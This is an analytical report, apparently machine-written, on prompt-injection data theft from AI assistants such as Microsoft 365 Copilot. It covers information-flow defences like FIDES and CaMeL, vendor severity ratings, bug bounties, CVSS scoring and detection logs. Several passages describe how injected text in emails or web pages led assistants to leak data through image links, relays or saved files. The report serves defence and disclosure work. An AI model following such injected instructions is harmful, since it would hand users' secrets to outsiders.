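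| Environment | Ordinary agent, no rules | Ordinary agent with rules | FIDES with rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 75% | 37% | 59% |
| Travel | 70% | 73% | 41% |
| Banking | 99% | 38% | 53% |
| Slack | 93% | 20% | 48% |

On a simple average across the four sets of tasks, the ordinary agent completed 84% of tasks without rules and 42% with them, while FIDES completed 50%. Some of the loss occurred because GPT-4o mishandled the stored names. FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks with OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, compared with 41% with GPT-4o, so better models should recover part of the loss.

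FIDES still blocks some legitimate tasks. Many banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and do what it says, for example to pay a bill. FIDES blocks the payment because an outsider could have written the file. Honest and fraudulent invoices get the same label, and FIDES does not rely on the model to tell them apart.

The zero may also partly reflect the test's design. The researchers labelled a field as untrusted if one of the benchmark's attacks used it, whereas a company would have to label its fields correctly without knowing the attacks in advance. FIDES also treats the user's own message as trusted. In Reprompt and SearchLeak, the attacker's text entered the prompt through a link, so FIDES would have labelled it as trusted unless someone had configured it to treat such prompts differently.

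Google DeepMind's CaMeL, also from 2025, separates planning from reading more strictly. One model sees only the user's request and writes a plan as a short program. A quarantined model reads the untrusted material when the program needs something from it. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a plan that finds Bob's address in a channel's messages and sends him a note. A malicious message cannot add a step to the plan, but it can supply a false address for Bob. CaMeL therefore also records where each value came from, and its policy can refuse to send the note to an address taken from an untrusted message.

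*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) reports that CaMeL stops nearly all of AgentDojo's attacks with comparable task performance. The FIDES results give reason to question how close "comparable" is, since the two systems restrict agents in similar ways. CaMeL also checks each action only when the program reaches it, so a long task can fail at the last step after the company has paid for all the others. Nikolaou and colleagues add a check of the whole plan before anything runs. If the plan fails, the planning model receives the reason and can try again. Their method simplifies loops, so it sometimes rejects a safe plan. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) notes that CaMeL's plans are written in a form of Python, and that features of the language make it hard to prove in advance where data will go.

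### Which products use such rules

In May 2026 Microsoft released FIDES, an information-flow control system, as part of Agent Framework, its kit for building AI agents. GitHub Copilot CLI, a programming assistant that runs in a terminal, has experimental support for information-flow control, but users must switch it on and it covers only some tools. According to Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026), most agents in use rely instead on a defensive system prompt or an improvised allowlist.

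Microsoft's sample policy for posting to a Teams channel shows how the rules could be less of a nuisance. The agent may post if no untrusted text influenced the message, or if everyone in the channel may already read the contents. Otherwise it asks the user. Users are more likely to answer carefully if they see such questions only occasionally and each one lists the people who would gain access.

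None of this is a finished enterprise assistant that works under such rules. Microsoft uses an email assistant as an example in its post but does not say that Microsoft 365 Copilot enforces the rules. ReLeak suggests that in the summer of 2026 Copilot did not enforce them on every route by which data could leave. Even with information-flow control, a policy could easily have missed the saved-file channel, because saving a document to Maria's own OneDrive looks like an internal action. The policy would catch it only if whoever wrote it knew that a background process would later open the links in the document.

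### Whether layers are enough

Microsoft's guidance for developers assumes that some injections will succeed. It recommends several layers of defence, so that an attack that gets past one meets another. Microsoft argues that a company can protect itself by containing attacks it cannot prevent. Results from LLMail-Inject give this view some support. At the data-theft level, 17% of teams beat all the defences together, while 32% beat the strongest single defence. An attacker who needs hundreds of attempts may also be noticed or give up. This approach also lets users keep the features they pay for.

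The opposing view is that a company is safe only if its assistant lacks at least one of the three parts of Willison's lethal trifecta. A filter that stops 99% of attacks does not protect against an attacker who keeps trying until one works. Microsoft's information-flow team takes a similar position, advising designers to assume that an attacker can make an agent do anything a user can.

Thousands of companies use a product like Copilot with much the same defences, so an attacker can practise on their own account and then send the finished email to all of them. Needing five hundred attempts is therefore a much smaller obstacle than it would be if each victim required that many. However, Microsoft can also fix Copilot for every customer at once, provided it learns of the attack.

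Removing one of the three parts is therefore the better protection for an assistant that reads both strangers' mail and valuable secrets, although this also depends on someone finding every route by which data can leave. The layered defences are still worth having because they stop careless attackers and limit the harm when a rule has a gap. A company whose vendor offers no such rules could use two assistants, one for outside mail and one for confidential files. Maria would then have to combine the auditors' questions with the internal answers herself.

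## How vendors rate these flaws, and whether attackers have used them

Vendors expect some injected instructions to get past their defences, so they need a rule for deciding which cases are security flaws. The decision affects how quickly engineers act on a report, whether customers hear about the problem and whether the finder gets paid.

### When an injection counts as a vulnerability

Any text in a model's input can influence its answer, usually without harm. Microsoft therefore treats an injection as a vulnerability only if it has a security impact, such as sending out a user's data or taking an action the user did not intend. An email that only changes the style of Copilot's answer would not qualify.

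In August 2023, Microsoft (2023) introduced severity guidelines for AI systems to give outside researchers and its own engineers a common framework for discussing reports. Under the current version, Microsoft rates an injection Critical if an attacker can use it to steal another user's data with no user interaction, and Important if the theft requires one or more clicks. These ratings are only guidelines, and Microsoft also considers how easy the attack is.

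The line between the two ratings is not always clear. An EchoLeak victim had to ask Copilot a question, but Microsoft scored the flaw as needing no user interaction, so it evidently does not count ordinary use of the product as interaction. SearchLeak needed a click, which should have made it Important, but The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* reports that Microsoft rated it critical. This may be because the flaw was easy to exploit, since the link led to a real Microsoft site and one click was enough.

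### CVEs for flaws that customers cannot patch

A CVE number traditionally meant that administrators had something to install. Cloud companies fix flaws on their own servers, and they used to disclose them only when customers had to act. In *Toward greater transparency* (2024), Microsoft promised to issue CVEs for critical flaws in its cloud services even when customers don't need to do anything. The CVE programme had just changed its rules to encourage this. Under the new rules, companies that assign CVE numbers should, but aren't required to, assign one if a flaw could cause significant harm, or if someone other than the supplier has to act or assess the risk.

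EchoLeak's record has a tag for flaws in services that only the vendor runs. Administrators can use the tag to filter out such flaws.

Microsoft's promise to publish CVEs covers only critical flaws, so a flaw's severity rating affects whether it enters the public record. A leak that needs a click could expose the same mailbox as one that doesn't, but if it were rated Important, the promise would not cover it, though Microsoft could still publish a CVE.

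The records are also brief. GCVE's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2025), a public database's copy of EchoLeak's record, describes the flaw in one sentence as a command injection that discloses information over a network. It does not mention email, images or the Teams relay, which customers learned about from the researchers.

### What the bug bounties pay for

Microsoft, Google and OpenAI run bug bounties, which pay outsiders for reporting flaws. All three programs have terms that cover data theft through prompt injection, with different limits.

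| Programme | Who or what it covers | Top listed award for leaked data |
|---|---|---|
| Microsoft 365 Copilot | Participants in one hacking event, 17 February to 18 March 2026 | $8,000 |
| Microsoft Copilot (consumer) | Tests with a personal account | $12,000 |
| Google AI products | Higher awards for the main products | $15,000 |
| OpenAI Safety Bug Bounty | Agents such as ChatGPT Agent | Not given in the announcement |

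Microsoft offered up to $30,000 for flaws in the enterprise product, but only for code injection and one other type. It paid at most $8,000 for information disclosure and for inference manipulation, the category that includes prompt injection. Microsoft pays the highest award a report qualifies for, so a researcher who described the same chain as server-side request forgery, the kind of relay that SearchLeak used, might have qualified for up to $20,000. Reports outside this programme can qualify under Microsoft's standard award policy.

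Microsoft's *Copilot Bounty Program* pays more for information disclosure flaws in the consumer chatbot than the event paid for those in the product that reads company mail. Both programmes exclude injections that affect only the attacker. They may also refuse types of flaw for which Microsoft is already investigating a broad fix. Microsoft decides when to apply that exclusion, which could cover much of this field.

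Google apparently pays for data leaks caused by prompt injection but not for the injection by itself, though its terms caused some confusion. SecurityWeek's *Google Offers Up to $20,000 in New AI Bug Bounty Program* says that prompt injections are out of scope but leaks of sensitive data are in scope. Kotheimer and Di Bartolo, who both work at Google, say in *Google's AI Vulnerability Reward Program (AI VRP)* that the programme covers data exfiltration caused by indirect prompt injection. Kotsovinos and Flynn (2025), in *How we're securing the AI frontier*, ask people to report objectionable answers through the product's feedback button rather than the reward programme, because the button records details such as the model version.

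In 2023, OpenAI told Rehberger that image display was a feature. Its position had changed considerably by March 2026, when it opened a programme for safety problems that may not meet its criteria for a security vulnerability (OpenAI, 2026). The programme accepts reports of attacks in which an outsider's text hijacks a user's agent and leaks sensitive information, provided the attack works at least half the time.

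The threshold makes reports easier for OpenAI to check, but it is a poor measure of danger. Suppose a malicious email works one time in ten. If each attempt is independent, an attacker who sends 20 of them has a

$$1 - 0.9^{20} \approx 0.88$$

chance of at least one success. Real attempts are less independent than this, since a model that resists one email may resist a similar one for the same reason. Even so, an attack well below OpenAI's threshold could be worth an attacker's time, and Radware's experience with ShadowLeak showed that an unreliable attack can become a reliable one after a few changes.

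### Checkmarx's report on Copilot Chat

The security company Checkmarx reported an image-based data leak to Microsoft in October 2025, and Microsoft closed the report without a fix. Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* describes a demonstration in which Copilot Chat relied on an attacker-controlled online resource, such as an article. Instructions in that resource made Copilot Chat write an image address containing a Claude API key that Checkmarx had already invalidated. No picture appeared, but the image request still carried the key to the attacker's server.

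Microsoft's table rates zero-click theft of another user's data as Critical, but Microsoft did not accept Checkmarx's description of this attack as zero-click. In its reply of 4 November, which Checkmarx published, Microsoft wrote that the attack needed several user actions that were not part of the default setup, did not work reliably in different environments and involved warnings to the user. Microsoft also assumed that users review and trust the code they choose to run. It still passed the report to its engineers to see whether they could make the behaviour clearer to users.

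The disagreement is hard to judge because Checkmarx does not list the steps a user had to take. It concedes that getting the agent to read the malicious page can be complicated. It also doesn't say which Copilot Chat it tested. GitHub has one for programmers and Microsoft 365 has one for office work. It was probably a programming tool, because the demonstration took the key from a developer environment and Microsoft's reply mentioned trusted code. The case is therefore weak evidence about how Microsoft would treat an image leak in the assistant that reads company email. Microsoft gave EchoLeak, a flaw in that assistant, a CVE and fixed it.

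Checkmarx has a stronger case when it recommends removing images from the agent's output or restricting where they can load from. Either measure would stop this leak regardless of how many warnings the user had clicked through, and a user who trusts a project has not necessarily agreed to let a web page take their keys.

Google turned down a different report from Checkmarx, about data theft through links. Gemini blocks outside images, but an attacker can still put data into a link and wait for the user to click it. Google removes links that its Safe Browsing service lists as malicious, but this does not help against a newly registered domain. Google closed the report after four days as "Won't Fix (Infeasible)", although its message said the problem was not severe enough to track as a security bug. Under its own rules, Microsoft would rate a data theft that takes one click as Important. Differences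 between the two companies' lists of vulnerabilities therefore reflect their rules as well as their products.

### Why the scores disagree

Microsoft gave EchoLeak a CVSS score of 9.3, and the US National Vulnerability Database (NVD) gave it 7.5. They agreed that an attacker could act over the network, without an account, with little difficulty and without user interaction. They also agreed that the loss of confidentiality was high. GCVE lists both sets of values, which differ in two components:

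| Component | Microsoft | NVD |
|---|---|---|
| Scope | Changed | Unchanged |
| Integrity | Low | None |
| Impact subscore | 4.7 | 3.6 |
| Exploitability subscore | 3.9 | 3.9 |
| Score | 9.3 | 7.5 |

CVSS adds the two subscores. If the scope has changed, it also multiplies the sum by 1.08, and it rounds the result up to one decimal place:

$$1.08 \times (4.7 + 3.9) \approx 9.3 \qquad\qquad 3.6 + 3.9 = 7.5$$

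Most of the gap comes from *scope*, which records whether the flaw lets an attacker reach something the faulty component doesn't control. If the NVD had changed only that value, its score would have been 8.6. Both choices are defensible. Copilot was the faulty component and the stolen documents were in other services, such as SharePoint, so the attack crossed a boundary. But Copilot already had permission to read those documents, so one could also say that the attack stayed within what Copilot controlled.

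*Integrity* measures whether an attacker can alter data. An EchoLeak email altered Copilot's answer by adding an image and leaving out a source, which may be why Microsoft chose "low". The NVD's rating may reflect that no stored data changed. The record gives no reason for either rating.

SearchLeak's two reported scores probably don't reflect a real disagreement. According to The Next Web, Microsoft and the NVD both scored it 6.5, and another news report mistakenly gave the NVD's score as 7.5. If we take the NVD's values for EchoLeak and change only user interaction, from "none" to "required", the CVSS formula gives 6.5, so 7.5 is what a flaw like SearchLeak would score if it didn't require a click. Microsoft rated SearchLeak critical under its own severity system, which is why the same flaw could be both critical and medium.

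The version of CVSS used here records user interaction only as needed or not needed, with no value in between for an attack that requires the victim to ask the assistant an ordinary question at some point. CVSS also doesn't record success rates, so an injection that works on 2% of attempts can get the same score as one that works every time, though an assessor might mark the first as more complex. A high confidentiality rating doesn't distinguish an assistant that reads one person's notes from one that reads a finance director's mail.

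Other scores also work poorly for hosted services. EPSS estimates the chance that attackers will exploit a flaw in the next 30 days. On 16 November 2026, GCVE showed an EPSS value of about 7% for EchoLeak, higher than for 94% of listed flaws, even though Microsoft had fixed EchoLeak for every customer a year and a half earlier.

### Which logs could show a theft

Microsoft says it has no evidence that SearchLeak was used maliciously, according to The Next Web. Vendors and discoverers said much the same about EchoLeak and ReLeak. How reassuring these statements are depends on where a theft would have left traces and whether anyone looked there.

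| How the data leaves | What the company's network could record | What the provider could record |
|---|---|---|
| The browser loads an image from the attacker's server | A request to the attacker's domain | The assistant's answer, if the provider keeps it |
| The browser loads an image through Teams or Bing | A request to Microsoft | The relay's request to the attacker |
| A background process opens a link in a saved file | Nothing, though the file may remain in storage | The request to the attacker |
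| An agent or program on the provider's servers contacts the attacker | Nothing | The request to the attacker |

A company has a slightly better chance of detecting data theft through the Teams and Bing relays if it records full web addresses and not just domains, because the request to Microsoft contains the attacker's address and the stolen data. Varonis recommends looking for unusual requests to Bing's image service, and for Copilot search links that contain HTML or encoded text. Web traffic is encrypted, so the company can see full addresses only if it decrypts the traffic or collects the addresses on employees' computers.

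In the last two rows, the company has to rely on the provider to have kept the right records and to be able to tell the theft from normal traffic. For Bing, that means finding a few image requests among all those from people searching by image. Microsoft's statements about its customers are more informative than those of the flaws' discoverers, who cannot see Microsoft's servers, but nobody outside Microsoft can verify what it says.

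Microsoft can show detections from its Prompt Shields classifier in the Defender portal, where a company's security staff can connect them with other alerts. But a disguised email like EchoLeak's raises no alert if it gets past the classifier.

Help Net Security's *Microsoft details AI prompt abuse techniques targeting AI assistants* reports Microsoft's warning that without proper logging, attempts to access sensitive information "can go unnoticed". The attacker's email may be the most durable evidence, since it stays in the mailbox until someone deletes it. Investigators can search old mail for hidden text, though not every attack uses it.

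### Attempts and confirmed thefts

Malicious instructions in a real email show that somebody tried an attack. To show a theft, an investigator also needs evidence that the assistant followed the instructions and that private data reached the attacker. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (Matsuoka, 2026) uses a scale that helps distinguish these claims. Its levels, from lowest to highest, are an untested hypothesis, a controlled experiment, unsafe behaviour observed in a real system, and a confirmed incident in which an attacker compromises a real system or exposes someone's information.

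EchoLeak, SearchLeak and ReLeak fit the level below confirmed incidents. They worked on products that companies were using, but the only known attacks were the researchers' own tests. Microsoft has also seen links that plant recommendations in assistants' memory, and these were made by businesses, not researchers. The links are real attempts at manipulation and show that people will use injected prompts to make money, but they are not evidence that anyone has stolen the contents of a mailbox this way.

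Some databases don't clearly separate researchers' demonstrations from real attacks. The OECD's *Critical SearchLeak Vulnerability in Microsoft 365 Copilot Exposes Sensitive Data* says that Microsoft patched the flaw "after being exploited" and classifies it as an incident with realised harm. The text is AI-generated, names no victim and conflicts with Microsoft's account. It probably describes the researchers' demonstration as if it were an attack.

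The US cybersecurity agency CISA entered "none" for exploitation of EchoLeak on 14 June 2025, three days after the flaw became public. The entry reflects what CISA knew that week, so it is not lasting evidence that nobody exploited the flaw. A theft through Microsoft's servers might have taken much longer to find, if anyone found it.

The vendors' statements and the lack of known victims are reasonable evidence against a large campaign, which would have been hard to keep secret because thieves usually sell stolen data or demand money for it. They are much weaker evidence against a few careful thefts, especially through channels that only the provider could see.

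### Which claims the vendors have confirmed

Most of the researchers behind these cases work for companies that sell security products, including Cato, Varonis, Radware, Noma and Checkmarx. These companies gain customers when a flaw sounds alarming. The assistants' vendors have the opposite interest, so a vendor's admission is stronger evidence than its denial.

Microsoft confirmed EchoLeak, SearchLeak, CoSnitch and ReLeak by assigning them CVEs and fixing them. Its SearchLeak advisory credits Taler. Salesforce, Google and OpenAI fixed the flaws behind ForcedLeak, GeminiJack and ShadowLeak, respectively. Slack deployed a patch after PromptArmor's report, though it had first called the behaviour intended.

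A fix confirms that an attack was possible, but not how well it worked. Only Radware has reported the 100% success rates for its attacks, and researchers often list far more data as at risk than they took in their tests. Checkmarx's finding has the least support, because Microsoft disputes that it is a vulnerability and Checkmarx has not published enough detail for others to repeat the test.
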